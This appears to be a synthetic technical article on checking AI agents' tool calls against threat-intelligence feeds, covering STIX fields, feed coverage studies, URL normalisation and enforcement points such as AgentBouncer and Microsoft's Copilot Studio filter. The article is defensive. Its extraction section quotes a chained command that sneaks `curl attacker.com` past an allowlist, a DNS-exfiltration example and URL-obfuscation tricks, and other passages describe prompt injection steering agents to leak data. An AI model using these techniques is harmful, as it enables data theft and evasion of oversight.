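# Threat-intelligence feeds in the risk scoring of AI agent actions

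## What feeds contain and what they can say about an agent's action

A threat-intelligence feed is a regularly updated, machine-readable list of domain names, web links, IP addresses, files and accounts that somebody has linked to attacks. *Survey and Analysis of DNS Filtering Components* (Magnusson, 2024) names open sources, commercial vendors and industry sharing groups among the suppliers, who draw their entries from network traffic, security logs and similar material. Network operators use feeds to keep people's computers away from known bad addresses. Feeds can also help judge the actions of an AI agent, a language model that carries out a task by calling tools such as a browser, a shell or an email client.

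Suppose a purchasing manager asks an agent to compare suppliers of cardboard packaging. The agent searches the web, and one result links to supplier-quotes.example, which imitates a real wholesaler's site to collect passwords. To open the site, the agent issues a tool call, a request that specifies a tool (here, the browser) and its arguments (here, the link). The call passes through an enforcement point, where the operator can inspect an action and stop it. The enforcement point may be the tool interface, a network proxy or a DNS resolver (the server that translates domain names into IP addresses).

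Software at the enforcement point takes the domain from the link and looks it up in the operator's copy of the feeds. A phishing feed lists the domain as an indicator, which is an observable value linked to an attack. The software has therefore found a match, meaning that a value in the agent's action equals an indicator or falls under one, as an IP address falls under a listed range. It then raises the action's risk score, the number or level that expresses how dangerous the operator judges the action to be and is used to decide how to handle it. If the score exceeds the operator's limit, the page does not load, and the agent receives an error and can go on to the next supplier.

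This sequence does not prove that the page would have caused harm. A feed entry provides only part of the information needed to estimate how likely harm is after a match.

### A feed entry, field by field

A widely known format for entries is STIX, short for Structured Threat Information Expression. The standards body OASIS (2021) approved version 2.1 in June 2021, building on specifications that the US Department of Homeland Security had contributed. An entry for the fake supplier could look like this, with invented values:

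```json
[
  {
    "type": "indicator",
    "spec_version": "2.1",
    "id": "indicator--3f0a6c1e-8b52-4d7e-9c41-5a2e7d90b614",
    "created": "2026-09-30T09:12:00.000Z",
    "modified": "2026-09-30T09:12:00.000Z",
    "name": "Fake packaging wholesaler",
    "indicator_types": ["malicious-activity"],
    "pattern": "[domain-name:value = 'supplier-quotes.example']",
    "pattern_type": "stix",
    "confidence": 85,
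    "valid_from": "2026-09-28T06:40:00Z",
    "valid_until": "2026-10-28T06:40:00Z"
  },
  {
    "type": "relationship",
    "spec_version": "2.1",
    "id": "relationship--b7d41f90-2c6a-4e13-8a5d-90c3e1f7a2b8",
    "created": "2026-09-30T09:12:00.000Z",
    "modified": "2026-09-30T09:12:00.000Z",
    "relationship_type": "indicates",
    "source_ref": "indicator--3f0a6c1e-8b52-4d7e-9c41-5a2e7d90b614",
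    "target_ref": "infrastructure--e92c5a47-71bd-4f06-b3e8-1d4a6c80f52e"
  },
  {
    "type": "infrastructure",
    "spec_version": "2.1",
    "id": "infrastructure--e92c5a47-71bd-4f06-b3e8-1d4a6c80f52e",
    "created": "2026-09-30T09:12:00.000Z",
    "modified": "2026-09-30T09:12:00.000Z",
    "name": "Copy of a wholesaler's site",
    "infrastructure_types": ["phishing"],
    "first_seen": "2026-09-28T06:40:00Z"
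  }
]
```

The `pattern` field contains the value to look up. OASIS's *STIX v2.1* (2025) defines `confidence` as how sure the creator of the entry is that the data are correct, on a scale from 0 to 100. This is easy to misread as the probability that the agent's action is harmful. For example, a creator can be nearly certain that a domain hosted a phishing page last week, while the agent is reading a genuine price list elsewhere on the same domain. If an entry has no `confidence` field, its confidence is unspecified, and software should not treat it as zero.

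`valid_from` and `valid_until` give the period in which the creator considers the indicator valid. An indicator without `valid_until` has no end date, so the operator needs a rule for when to expire it. The creator can also permanently revoke an indicator, and OASIS lets each implementation decide how to handle revoked ones.

The Indicator object has no field for the date of first sighting, and its `indicator_types` are broad. The suggested values are anomalous-activity, anonymization, benign, compromised, malicious-activity, attribution and unknown. The "phishing" label and the `first_seen` date are in a separate Infrastructure object, which a Relationship object links to the Indicator. An import script that keeps only Indicator objects therefore loses what kind of threat the domain poses and how long it has been active. In the sample, `first_seen` is two days before `created`, and a lookup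 during those two days would have found nothing.

Apart from bookkeeping fields, the standard requires an indicator to have only a pattern, the pattern's language and a start date. Type, confidence and end date are optional, so an entry can conform to the standard and still lack most of what a risk score needs. *Indicators of Compromise (IoCs) and Their Role in Attack Defence* (Paine, Whitehouse and colleagues, 2023) describes an indicator as of little use without context, such as its role in the attack, its last sighting and its expected lifetime. This context lets a defender choose between logging, monitoring and blocking. In the experience of Paine and colleagues, whose paper was published as RFC 9424 by the Internet Engineering Task Force, which develops the internet's technical standards, those who share indicators often remove the context for privacy reasons, and do so more in large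 groups whose members do not trust one another much.

### How cheaply an attacker can change each indicator

Paine and colleagues order indicators by how hard they are for an attacker to change, in a scheme known as the Pyramid of Pain. File hashes, which are short fingerprints computed from a file's content, are at the bottom, followed by IP addresses and then domain names. The top three levels, which amount to behaviour, are traces on the network or the machine, the attacker's tools, and the attacker's methods. URLs have no level of their own, but they fit best near the bottom because anyone who controls a site can move a page to a new path without buying anything.

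| Indicator | What the attacker must do to escape it | What else a match can catch |
|---|---|---|
| File hash | Recompile the code or make a trivial change to the file | Practically nothing |
| URL | Move the page to another path | Little, unless the attacker has altered a legitimate page |
| IP address | Find a new address or provider, and change any code that contains the old address | Other sites and users behind the same address |
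| Domain name | Register a new name that still convinces victims | The legitimate parts of a hijacked site |
| Behaviour | Switch tools or rework the attack | Harmless software that acts in a similar way |

The indicators that are hardest for an attacker to change are generally also the least precise. A hash match is virtually never wrong if the hash function is sound, but an attacker can avoid a match by changing one byte. An IP address at a cloud provider may pass from one customer to another, and many unrelated systems can share one address at the same time.

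The ordering rests on practitioners' experience, and Paine and colleagues call for research into the exact trade-offs. They report that in January 2023 AlienVault, an open community for sharing threat intelligence, held about 64.8 million domain names, 5.4 million IPv4 addresses and 5.5 million SHA-256 hashes. This does not fit the ordering, because if counts fell steadily towards the top of the pyramid, there would be fewer domain names than IP addresses. They suspect that there are so many domain names because some malware generates them by algorithm, and because attackers register names to impersonate real organisations and replace them as defenders confiscate them. The fake wholesaler would be an example of the second cause.

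For an agent, the types also differ in when a lookup is possible. A domain or URL appears in the tool call, so it can be checked before anything has happened. A hash can be computed only once the software has a copy of the file, so that check has to come between the download and the agent's first use of the file. Checking behaviour takes more than a single lookup, because it means comparing a series of actions with a known pattern. For agents that write code, software packages are another type of value to check. Datadog, which sells monitoring software, includes package names with version numbers among the indicators in its *Threat Intelligence* documentation. It warns that a package's contents can vary even under the same version number, so a match on the name is weaker than a match on the file's hash.

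### The destination and the party that acts

An operator can use a feed to check whether an action's destination is malicious and, separately, whether the party behind the action is a known bad actor. In the supplier case, only the destination is listed. The manager gave an ordinary instruction, and a rule that lowered the manager's standing because of the match would punish the intended victim.

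The real wholesaler faces the reverse case. An unfamiliar agent visits its web shop from an IP address that a feed lists as part of a botnet, a group of hijacked computers under one controller. The wholesaler knows its own pages are harmless but wants to know who sent the agent.

STIX roughly separates what is malicious from who is responsible. Its type `malicious-activity` covers suspected malicious objects and activity, while `attribution` covers patterns of behaviour that point to a particular attacker or campaign. Products tend to mix the two. Microsoft's *Tutorial* on threat-intelligence policies describes the feature as blocking "known bad actors", although it blocks web destinations. Datadog's single table of categories includes scanners, proxies and exit points of the anonymity network Tor (who is connecting) as well as malicious packages and cryptocurrency-mining addresses (what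 a machine fetches or contacts).

Datadog assigns each category in that table one of three intents (benign, suspicious or malicious), and only the malware and mining categories count as malicious. Categories that describe the connecting party's address are rated suspicious at most, and corporate VPNs are rated benign. These lower ratings make sense because an IP address's reputation often changes within a day and many hosts may share the address. An operator who gives a listed source address the same weight as a listed phishing domain will treat many innocent users as attackers. The problem is worse with agents because the acting party could be the user who set the task, the company that runs the agent or the agent software itself, and an IP address is rarely enough to distinguish them.

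### Blocking, investigating and scoring

The simplest use of a match is to block the action outright. A Microsoft service blocks domains and URLs that Microsoft's and other suppliers' feeds link with high confidence to malware distribution, phishing or the servers that control infected machines. Traffic without a match passes unless another policy stops it. Administrators can enter exceptions for false matches (matches on harmless actions). The service checks full URLs only if the customer lets it decrypt the traffic. Otherwise, an entry for one bad page on a good site has no effect. Paine and colleagues report that the UK National Cyber Security Centre's DNS filter for the public sector blocked more than 160 million of 602 billion queries in 2021, or roughly one in 3,800.

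A match can instead inform a later investigation. Datadog attaches matches to a customer's logs, where responders weigh them with other evidence, and it advises against blocking on IP or domain intelligence alone, with few exceptions. A 2021 study summarised by Magnusson gives some support for this caution. Fejrskov and colleagues compared DNS blocklists with records of actual network connections. Only a tiny share of DNS responses matched an entry, and many of the connections that blocking would have cut were potentially harmless, for example because one web server hosted both good and bad sites.

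Microsoft and Datadog disagree less than they seem to. Microsoft limits blocking to high-confidence entries about destinations, while much of Datadog's material concerns the addresses of connecting parties. It is reasonable to block a fresh phishing domain with a confidence of 85, as in the supplier case. A listed cloud address with no date or threat type may deserve some weight in the risk score, but not enough to justify blocking.

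A risk score gives threat intelligence some weight in a decision, an idea that predates AI agents. *Zero Trust Architecture*, published by the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) in August 2020, describes a system that does not trust a request merely because of where it comes from on the network. A policy engine decides on each request, and an enforcement point carries out the decision. The engine's inputs include threat-intelligence feeds, the request itself, data about the requester and the device, and the resource's requirements. NIST notes that the feeds are probably the only input controlled by an outside service.

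The engine can combine these inputs in two ways. It can require a request to meet every criterion on a list and refuse it if it fails one. Or it can multiply each input by a weight, add up the results and compare the sum with a threshold for that resource. Unlike a risk score, NIST's sum measures confidence, so a higher value is better. Scoring also allows partial access, such as permission to read a file but not change it. The engine can judge each request alone or consider the requester's recent history. NIST prefers using history where the infrastructure permits it, because an attacker who stays within a stolen account's permissions may look normal in any single request.

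This design needs few changes to cover agents. NIST's requesters include software processes as well as people, and its feeds bear on both questions. They list things that the organisation's machines should not reach, and they can expose a device that has been contacting suspected control servers. The main difference is that NIST wrote about access to an organisation's own resources, whereas much of an agent's work, like the supplier search, involves requests to the open web.

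### What differs when the requester is an agent

The standards and product pages above describe feeds for networks, devices and human users. Claims about what changes with agents are inferred from how agents work, and no measurements support them so far.

The most obvious difference from human browsing is volume. A person comparing suppliers opens a handful of pages and glances at the address bar, while an agent may open dozens in a few minutes with nobody watching. At that volume, even a small error rate produces many false matches. If one harmless request in 10,000 produced a false match, an operator whose agents made a million requests a day would have 100 false matches a day. Nobody can review each one carefully while the agents wait, so most decisions have to be automatic.

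The model also chooses which addresses to visit. An employee who types a known supplier's address has some reason to trust it, and the employer can take that choice as some evidence that the address is safe. An agent takes links from search results, other pages or its own guess at a company's domain. The manager's honest intention is therefore evidence that the task is legitimate, but says little about whether an individual link is safe. Finding no match in a feed doesn't show that the link is safe either, because feeds contain only what somebody has already discovered, a limit that Microsoft openly acknowledges.

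A page can also steer an agent just by being read, whereas a phishing page usually harms a person only if they type in a password. Prompt injection is text planted in content an agent reads that makes it follow an attacker's instructions. Such text might tell the agent to send the manager's price list to an outside address. The lookup therefore has to happen before the page's content reaches the model. If the operator lets a doubtful page through, the agent's later actions in the same task should also get a higher score, even if their own destinations match nothing in the feeds.

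Prompt injection also makes a feed's threat types a poorer match for an agent's risks. A phishing entry lists a page that could steal people's passwords, but an agent that holds no credentials may read that page without harm. But an attacker can plant instructions for the agent in a customer review on a reputable marketplace, and feeds would have no good reason to list that marketplace's domain.

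## Choosing feeds and measuring their coverage

When an operator checks agents' actions against a feed, the check can stop only what the feed already lists. Coverage, the share of malicious values that a feed lists at the moment an agent meets them, therefore matters most to a buyer. It is also the hardest property to measure, because nobody has a complete list of malicious domains to compare a feed with. Researchers instead compare feeds with one another or with attacks on live networks. Nearly all of their evidence comes from ordinary networks, and much of it concerns IP addresses. Only one of the tests below, by the security company LayerX, involved AI browsers.

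### Six measures of a feed

*Reading the Tea Leaves* (Li, Dunn and colleagues, 2019) defined six measures for comparing feeds. An operator might be choosing between two phishing feeds, for example. In one month, feed A lists 1,000 domains, feed B lists 400, and 100 domains appear in both.

| Measure | How to calculate it | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Volume | Number of entries in the period | A has 1,000 and B has 400 |
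| Differential contribution | Share of one feed's entries that another feed lacks | 300 of B's 400 entries (75%) are missing from A; the other 25% are the overlap |
| Exclusive contribution | Share of a feed's entries that appear in no other feed under comparison | A third feed lists 60 of those 300 entries, so 240 of B's 400 (60%) are exclusive |
| Latency | Time from an entry's first appearance in any feed to its appearance in this one | A lists a domain on Monday at 09:00 and B on Wednesday at 09:00, so the latency is zero for A and 48 hours for B |
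| Accuracy | Share of entries that belong in the feed | 20 of A's 1,000 entries are well-known harmless sites, so its accuracy is at most 98% |
| Coverage | Share of malicious values that the feed lists | Agents met 50 malicious domains and A already listed 15 of them, so its coverage is 30% |

A buyer learns little from a feed's volume alone. In Li and colleagues' data, one feed of scanning addresses had 361,004 entries and another had 1,572. A third feed, of malware servers, held 1,440 addresses but gained only 1.3 a day, so most of its content was old. For phishing, where attackers change domains quickly, the number of new entries per day is more useful than the total.

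Differential contribution depends on the direction of the comparison. A customer of A who adds B gains 300 domains, while a customer of B who adds A gains 900. (The buyer's example that Li and colleagues give has the two feeds the wrong way round.)

Latency is easy to confuse with listing delay, which is measured from the start of malicious use. If the attacker in the table began using the domain on the Saturday at 09:00, the listing delay was 48 hours for A and 96 for B. A latency of zero means only that no other feed in the comparison listed the entry sooner. Latency is undefined for entries that appear in only one feed, as most do.

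The table gives accuracy as "at most" a certain value because nobody can verify every entry. Li and colleagues counted an entry as inaccurate only if it was clearly wrong or unusable, such as the address of a very popular website, so the remaining entries could still contain errors.

### How little feeds overlap

Li and colleagues collected 47 feeds of IP addresses and eight feeds of file hashes every hour from December 2017 to July 2018. They grouped the address feeds by type of threat and, within each type, measured the share of addresses that appeared in only one feed. This share was 73% for scanning, 88% for password guessing, and over 97% for malware servers, botnets, exploit attempts and spam. They repeated the analysis on data from two years apart and got consistent results.

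They also found obvious errors, such as addresses of very popular websites in 21 of the 47 feeds. A spam feed from AlienVault with about 11,000 addresses included 1,040 that belonged to large content delivery networks, which serve many unrelated websites from the same addresses. Those entries may do little damage in a mail filter, but an agent that compares suppliers opens sites on such networks all day, so an operator who reused the feed to check web destinations could expect many false matches. In *A SoK for SoCs*, Vasan, Benkraouda and colleagues (2026) surveyed 18 practitioners who produce threat intelligence, and 13 named separating attackers' addresses from harmless ones as a challenge. The paper cites a 2020 evaluation of feed quality by Griffioen, Booij and Doerr for the consequences of such errors.

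Expensive feeds overlap with each other no more than free ones do. Bouwman, Griffioen and colleagues compared two market-leading vendors in *A different cup of TI?* (2020). Such vendors charged roughly $100,000 to $650,000 a year. Their licences forbid customers to share the data, so one researcher analysed it while working as an intern at a customer. Both vendors claimed to track the same 22 attacker groups, but on average only 2.8% of a group's IP addresses, 4.0% of its domains and 2.5% of its file hashes appeared in both feeds. The highest overlap for any group was 21%, for IP addresses. Fewer than 1% of the vendors' indicators appeared in any of four large open feeds.

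When both vendors listed an indicator, the slower one listed it more than a month later on average. This is weak evidence about typical delays because it comes from only 16 indicators that one vendor listed first and 28 that the other listed first.

Bouwman and colleagues also interviewed 14 professionals who used paid intelligence. These customers wanted carefully selected data that saved their analysts time, and they worried much less about missed threats. They also valued the vendors' written reports and being able to ask the vendors' staff questions. An operator of agents gets less from these benefits because most of its decisions are automatic, so a feed that is worth its price to a security team may not be worth buying to check tool calls.

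A buyer can roughly estimate a feed's coverage from its overlap with another feed, much as ecologists estimate an animal population from two rounds of trapping. If feeds A and B find malicious domains independently, B's entries are effectively a random sample of all malicious domains, so the share of them that A also lists estimates A's coverage. In the example, A lists 100 of B's 400 entries, so its coverage would be about 25%, and B lists 100 of A's 1,000, so its coverage would be about 10%. Bouwman and colleagues found that, over five months, one vendor listed 13% of the other's indicators, while the other listed 1.3% of the first's. By this method, the two feeds covered about 13% and 1.3% of the threats they were both looking for.

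The coverage estimate is wrong if the feeds are not independent. It is too low when the feeds cover different attackers, because they overlap less, and too high when they draw on the same source, because they overlap more.

Some vendors draw on the same source. Galloway, Chang and colleagues (2026), in *Actively Understanding the Dynamics and Risks of the Threat Intelligence Ecosystem*, sent 30 security vendors harmless programs that looked suspicious. Each time somebody ran a program, it contacted a unique domain name and left a new copy of itself. The domain name encoded the chain of earlier runs, so the researchers could trace where a program and its indicators had travelled. Twenty vendors (67%) ran the program in a sandbox, an isolated machine for analysing software, but only five (17%) shared what they extracted. Four vendors acted as hubs that redistributed much of the material.

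According to Galloway and colleagues' conference slides, five of the nine antivirus companies took data from intelligence platforms, and only one shared any. Two feeds that list the same domain may therefore be repeating a single sighting. Blocking took between one hour and ten days after submission. The researchers used free, public services and submitted files rather than phishing pages, so the percentages may not hold for paid feeds of domains.

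### Coverage of what a network actually meets

The comparisons so far count entries, but an entry protects an agent only if the agent encounters that address. Deri and Fusco (2023), in *Evaluating IP Blacklists Effectiveness*, tested six free blocklists on live traffic in European networks, including a service provider with about 5,000 servers and a university with over 100,000 public addresses. They treated any computer that contacted at least 128 unused addresses in a day as certain to be scanning for weaknesses, then checked these scanners against blocklists downloaded the same day.

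The best list, from the Stratosphere project, contained 50.5% of the scanners seen at the service provider but only 14.6% of those seen at the university, so a buyer cannot assume that another organisation's results will apply to its own network. Three of the lists contained almost none of the scanners. One of these, Feodo Tracker, tracks only certain types of malware, so its low coverage does not indicate poor quality. All these figures are for computers that contacted the networks from outside, and coverage may differ for sites that an agent visits.

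Adding two more lists to Stratosphere's raised the match rate at the service provider only from 50.5% to 50.9%, even though the lists had few entries in common. One of the added lists, Emerging Threats, matched 13.6% of the scanners on its own, so Stratosphere's list already included nearly all of the scanners it caught. The two added lists contained many addresses that Stratosphere's lacked, but hardly any of those addresses belonged to scanners that visited the network. The entries unique to a feed are therefore useful to a buyer only if they include addresses that the buyer's agents encounter.

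Estimating coverage from overlap can give too high a figure. In the same data, Stratosphere listed more than 95% of the scanners that Emerging Threats matched, so the trapping method would put Stratosphere's coverage above 95%, but the measured figure was 50.5%. A likely reason is that conspicuous scanners end up on several lists while quieter ones end up on none.

*TIBlender* (Nakano, Koide and Chiba, 2026) gives an idea of how much public feeds miss. It describes a system of language-model agents that searches X, Reddit, Telegram and Discord for signs of attacks and writes reports with indicators. The agents produce threat intelligence, and no feed is used to judge their actions. The system wrote 8,288 reports over 31 days in March and April 2026. Nakano and colleagues compared its indicators with six public feeds, counting for each feed only the types of indicator it covers, and found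 that between 83.0% and 99.6% were absent, depending on the feed. PhishTank, a public list of phishing pages, contained 227 (4.6%) of 4,914 phishing domains and URLs.

Errors in TIBlender's reports are unlikely to explain most of the cases in which none of a report's indicators appeared in any of the six feeds. Two security engineers reviewed 500 of these unmatched reports and 500 reports with at least one indicator in the feeds. They judged that 1.8% of the unmatched reports and 2.2% of the matched ones described no real threat that a defender could act on. They found an unsupported indicator in 4.0% of the unmatched reports and 3.6% of the matched ones. The review is weaker evidence for phishing domains, because about half of all TIBlender's reports concerned software vulnerabilities.

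Monitoring social media would not replace the feeds, either. When an indicator appeared both in TIBlender's output and in a public feed, TIBlender had it first in only 18.7% of cases.

### When a browser does not consult a list

A feed with excellent coverage is useless if the agent's software never checks it. In 2025, LayerX tested three AI browsers (Comet, Genspark and Dia) and two conventional ones (Chrome and Edge). LayerX sells a browser add-on that competes with their built-in protection. It took the 100 most recent phishing pages from public sources such as OpenPhish and PhishTank, tried to open them all in each browser, and counted how many were blocked.

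| Browser | Phishing pages blocked, of 100 |
|---|---|
| Edge | 54 |
| Chrome | 47 |
| Dia | 46 |
| Comet | 7 |
| Genspark | 7 |

The low result for Comet and Genspark may reflect the lack of a list rather than a poor one. All five browsers are built on Google's Chromium code, which can show a red warning when a page is on a list of known bad addresses and a white one when the connection has a fault, such as an invalid security certificate. Comet and Genspark showed no red warnings, and every page they stopped had a connection fault. LayerX inferred from this behaviour that neither browser used Google's Safe Browsing lists, although Comet's settings page showed standard Safe Browsing as switched on. Dia agreed with Chrome on 97% of the pages, as one would expect if both consulted the same Google lists.

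Edge's lead over Chrome could be chance. The two browsers gave the same result on about 80 pages, while Edge did better on about 14 and Chrome on about 6. (Because of rounding, these counts give a lead of eight pages instead of seven.) If the browsers were equally good, each of the 20 pages where they differed would be like a coin toss, and a split at least as uneven as 14 to 6 would occur about 12% of the time. This evidence is therefore too weak for an operator to use in choosing between Edge and Chrome. The gap of 40 pages between Chrome and Comet is far too large for chance to explain.

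Somebody had already reported every page in the sample to a public list. Coverage of unreported pages may well be lower, and LayerX writes that all the browsers failed on a new, unknown phishing link. The sample also contained no harmless pages, so the test could not measure false matches, and a browser that blocked every page would have scored 100. This also makes it hard to judge LayerX's claim that its own add-on detects phishing with 98% accuracy.

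LayerX also states that Comet and Genspark are up to 85% more vulnerable than Chrome, which does not follow from its figures. They let through 93 pages, 75% more than Chrome's 53. The 85% matches how many fewer pages they blocked than Chrome.

Of these studies, LayerX's is the closest to feeds applied to agents, although it tested whether pages opened, not what an agent did on them. Browser makers can add list lookups in an update, so the scores may not describe current versions. An operator can check its own setup in a few minutes by adding a harmless domain it owns to its local copy of the feed and telling an agent to open that domain. If the page loads, the agent's traffic is bypassing the check.

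### Trialling two feeds before buying

Because coverage varied so much between networks, a buyer should test candidate feeds on its own agents' traffic. None of the studies above describes such a test for agents, so the following procedure adapts their methods.

1. Decide what the feed is for and ask each vendor for matching data. To check the sites that agents visit, the operator needs domains and URLs with dates and threat types. A long list of scanning addresses will not help. The trial licence should let the operator download the feed and keep old copies. Looking up each URL on the vendor's server instead could reveal what the agents are working on.

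2. Log every destination that the agents request for at least four weeks, with the exact time and the full URL. The log must include requests that no current control flags, since those are where a new feed could add something.

3. Save a copy of both feeds at every update and match each request against the copies that existed at that moment. Deri and Fusco did this with daily lists. If the operator instead checked last month's log against today's feed, the feed would get credit for domains that it listed only after the agents had visited them.

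4. Collect a reference set of malicious destinations without using either feed. Sources include past incidents, a manual review of unfamiliar domains in the log, and a second look at the log a few weeks later, when other sources may have identified more bad sites. Agents may meet few malicious sites in a month, so the operator can add phishing links from its own mail filter and look them up as they arrive, without opening them. Links from public lists are a poor choice, because they favour any feed that copies those lists.

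5. Have a reviewer judge every match as harmful, harmless or unclear without knowing which feed produced it. If there are too many, a random sample from each feed will do.

6. Count malicious destinations caught and harmless actions stopped, for each feed alone and for the two together.

Suppose the agents make a million requests during the trial and the reference set contains 60 malicious domains. The counts might look like this:

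| | Malicious domains listed in time, of 60 | Coverage | Harmless actions matched |
|---|---|---|---|
| Feed A | 27 | 45% | 40 |
| Feed B | 21 | 35% | 8 |
| Both feeds together | 33 | 55% | 48 |

Feed A appears to have better coverage, but the evidence is weak. Fifteen domains are in both feeds, 12 only in A and 6 only in B. If the feeds had equal coverage, a split at least as uneven as 12 to 6 would occur about 24% of the time. With only 60 domains in the reference set, A's coverage could plausibly be anywhere from roughly 32% to 58%. If the choice depends on the difference between the feeds, the operator should extend the trial until the reference set is several times larger.

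The difference in false matches is clearer. Feed B catches 21 malicious domains and stops 8 harmless actions. Adding A would catch 12 more domains but stop 40 more harmless actions. Adding A may be worthwhile if a wrongly stopped action only makes an agent move on to the next supplier. If it interrupts a payment or a software release, the operator might buy only B, or buy both and let a match in A raise the risk score without blocking the action.

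Even with both feeds, the agents in this example would reach 27 of the 60 malicious domains without a match. The operator should consider that number when deciding what to buy, because other controls would still have to catch those domains.

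## Extracting destinations from agent actions and checking them

To compare an agent's action with a feed, the operator's software first has to work out which destinations the action will contact. This is easy when a browser tool receives a plain link but harder when the agent runs a shell command, because the command may follow a redirect or start a script that opens its own connections.

Researchers have tested how completely various controls cover agents' actions, but none of those tests measured feed lookups. Microsoft documents a service that applies feeds to agents' traffic, but the documentation describes settings and gives no results. The lookup procedure follows ordinary web practice.

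### From a tool call to a result

Suppose the purchasing manager's agent reads an email with a shortened link to a price list. It decides to download the file and issues this tool call:

```json
{
  "tool": "shell",
  "arguments": {
    "command": "mkdir -p quotes && curl -sL -o quotes/prices.xlsx HTTPS://Lnk.Example:443/a/../pk7"
  }
}
```

The program `curl` downloads content from web addresses, and the `L` in its options makes it follow redirects. The short link redirects to supplier-quotes.example, the fake wholesaler's site listed in the operator's phishing feed. The software can check the download in six steps.

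1. Parse the arguments. The line contains two commands, one that creates a folder and one that contacts a web address, so the software has to parse all of it. Kim, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI*, describe what happened when the open-source agent AutoGPT compared only the first word of a line with its list of permitted commands. A line such as `cat file; curl attacker.com` passed because it began with `cat`. Some commands contain no address at all, such as `python fetch.py`. The software should record their destination as unknown and leave the check to another enforcement point.

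2. Normalise the URL. One address can have many spellings, and a feed usually lists only one. The software changes the host name to lower case, removes port 443 (the default for HTTPS) and simplifies the path, which gives `https://lnk.example/pk7`. It keeps the case of the letters in the path, because many servers distinguish between them. It also converts unusual spellings of IP addresses. For example, `http://3405803800/` leads to 203.0.113.24. In `https://real-wholesaler.example@supplier-quotes.example/`, the part before the @ is only a user name, and the request goes to the fake wholesaler.

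3. Look up the URL and the domain. The software tries the full URL, then the host name, then any parent domain that belongs to the same owner. It does this before it contacts anything, including the DNS. An attacker who runs the DNS server for attacker.example receives every query for a name under that domain. A prompt injection could therefore make an agent leak a price by asking for `price-4200.attacker.example`, even if the agent never connects to the site.

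4. Resolve the domain to an IP address and look that up too. The software must then connect to the same address it checked, because a second DNS query might return a different one.

5. Treat each redirect as a new destination. The software lets the request go to the shortening service, reads the address in the reply, and repeats steps 2 to 4 before it allows the next request. It could instead open the short link itself in advance to find out where it leads. That is less reliable, because the attacker's server can send the checking software to a harmless page and the agent to a harmful one. It may also use up a link that works only once.

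6. Return a result to the software that decides on the action.

In the example, the lookups would run in this order:

| Value | Result |
|---|---|
| `https://lnk.example/pk7` | No match |
| `lnk.example` | No match |
| `198.51.100.7` (the shortening service) | No match |
| `https://supplier-quotes.example/files/prices.xlsx` | No match |
| `supplier-quotes.example` | Match: phishing, confidence 85 |

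The first three lookups find nothing because the shortening service is legitimate. The software stops at the fifth, before anything has contacted the fake wholesaler, and returns a record like this one:

```json
{
  "outcome": "match",
  "value": "supplier-quotes.example",
  "value_type": "domain",
  "reached_through": "https://lnk.example/pk7",
  "indicator_id": "indicator--3f0a6c1e-8b52-4d7e-9c41-5a2e7d90b614",
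  "threat_type": "phishing",
  "confidence": 85,
  "valid_until": "2026-10-28T06:40:00Z",
  "feed_copy_from": "2026-10-07T08:00:00Z"
}
```

The record keeps the type, confidence and dates for the later decision. The `outcome` field should have separate values for "no match", "lookup failed" and "destination unknown". If the software reports all three as "no match", the operator will treat unchecked actions as if they had passed.

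### What each enforcement point can inspect

The redirect in step 5 happens inside `curl`, after the tool interface has approved the command. An operator who checks only tool calls would look up lnk.example, find nothing and allow the download. Other enforcement points can inspect the redirect but lack other information.

| Enforcement point | Available information | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
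| Tool interface | Tool, arguments and often the user's task | Redirects, and connections that a script or tool opens by itself |
| Browser | Full URL of every page, including redirects that a page's own code triggers | Traffic from the shell and other tools |
| Network proxy that decrypts traffic | Domain, full URL and content of each web request | The task behind the request, and any traffic that avoids the proxy |
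| Network proxy that does not decrypt | Usually the domain and port | The page's path and the content |
| DNS resolver | Domain name | The path, connections straight to an IP address, and queries to other resolvers |
| Operating-system kernel | IP address, port and the program that connects | The domain, URL and encrypted content |

*AgentBouncer* (Joos and Pradel, 2026) shows why the kernel's information is not enough by itself. The system protects coding agents by intercepting system calls, which are a program's requests to the operating system, such as to open a file or a connection. The system call for a network connection contains only an IP address and a port, and encryption usually hides the content. An agent that installs a package from a public registry and an agent that sends stolen data to an attacker both appear to connect to some address on port 443.

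AgentBouncer recovers the missing information in two stages. It first blocks every outgoing connection except those to its own proxy or within the same machine, so programs cannot bypass the proxy. The proxy then decrypts each web request and extracts the method, the URL and the request body. The method indicates whether the program is fetching or sending something, and the body contains what it sends. With these details, AgentBouncer can distinguish a package download from an upload of passwords. For connections that do not use web protocols, it still has only the destination's host and port.

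AgentBouncer settles routine cases with fixed rules and uses a language model to judge whether each remaining request is safe and necessary for the task. It does not consult feeds. In a test with 340 attacks, it reduced the success rate from 99.41% to 10.59%. It added an average of 47 seconds and $0.0036 in model fees to each harmless task. These figures cover the whole system, so they do not measure how much a feed lookup would catch or how long it would take.

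An operator could add a feed to this design fairly easily. The fixed rules can cover every URL that starts with a given prefix, and a rule that denies a request overrides one that allows it, so each domain in the feed could become a deny rule. However, AgentBouncer loads its rules when a run starts, so a domain added to the feed during a run would have no effect until the next one.

Joos and Pradel's attacks also show the limits of checking only tool calls. In one of them, a tool called `validate_patch` does what its description promises but also silently deletes a system file. Both the call and the tool's output look harmless. A malicious tool could contact an attacker's server in the same way, and a lookup based on the call's arguments would not include that server's address.

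### Microsoft's filter for Copilot Studio agents

Microsoft's service for blocking high-confidence entries is part of Global Secure Access, a set of network controls for employees' web traffic. Microsoft also offers these controls for agents that customers build in its Copilot Studio.

An administrator first turns on forwarding for a group of agents, which sends their requests through Microsoft's proxy service. Forwarding covers plain HTTP requests, custom connectors and connections to tool servers that use the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for linking agents to tools. A connector links an agent to another service, such as Slack. Custom connectors created before forwarding was turned on keep their old route until somebody edits and saves them, so it is easy to miss one and leave it unprotected.

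The administrator then creates a threat-intelligence policy and links it to the baseline profile, a set of rules that applies to the whole organisation. Microsoft warns that without a linked policy, the service records the agents' traffic but blocks nothing. Agents cannot have their own profiles, so the operator cannot set stricter rules for an agent that makes payments than for one that reads public pages.

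A new policy starts with one rule, the block on severe, high-confidence threats described earlier. Microsoft sets the default action for everything else to "Allow", which passes the request to the next control. Web content filtering comes before threat intelligence, and file-type rules come after it. If a Copilot Studio agent opened the short link, the request to the shortening service would match nothing and continue to the file-type rules. The redirect would then produce a second request, which Microsoft's service would block if its feeds listed the fake wholesaler.

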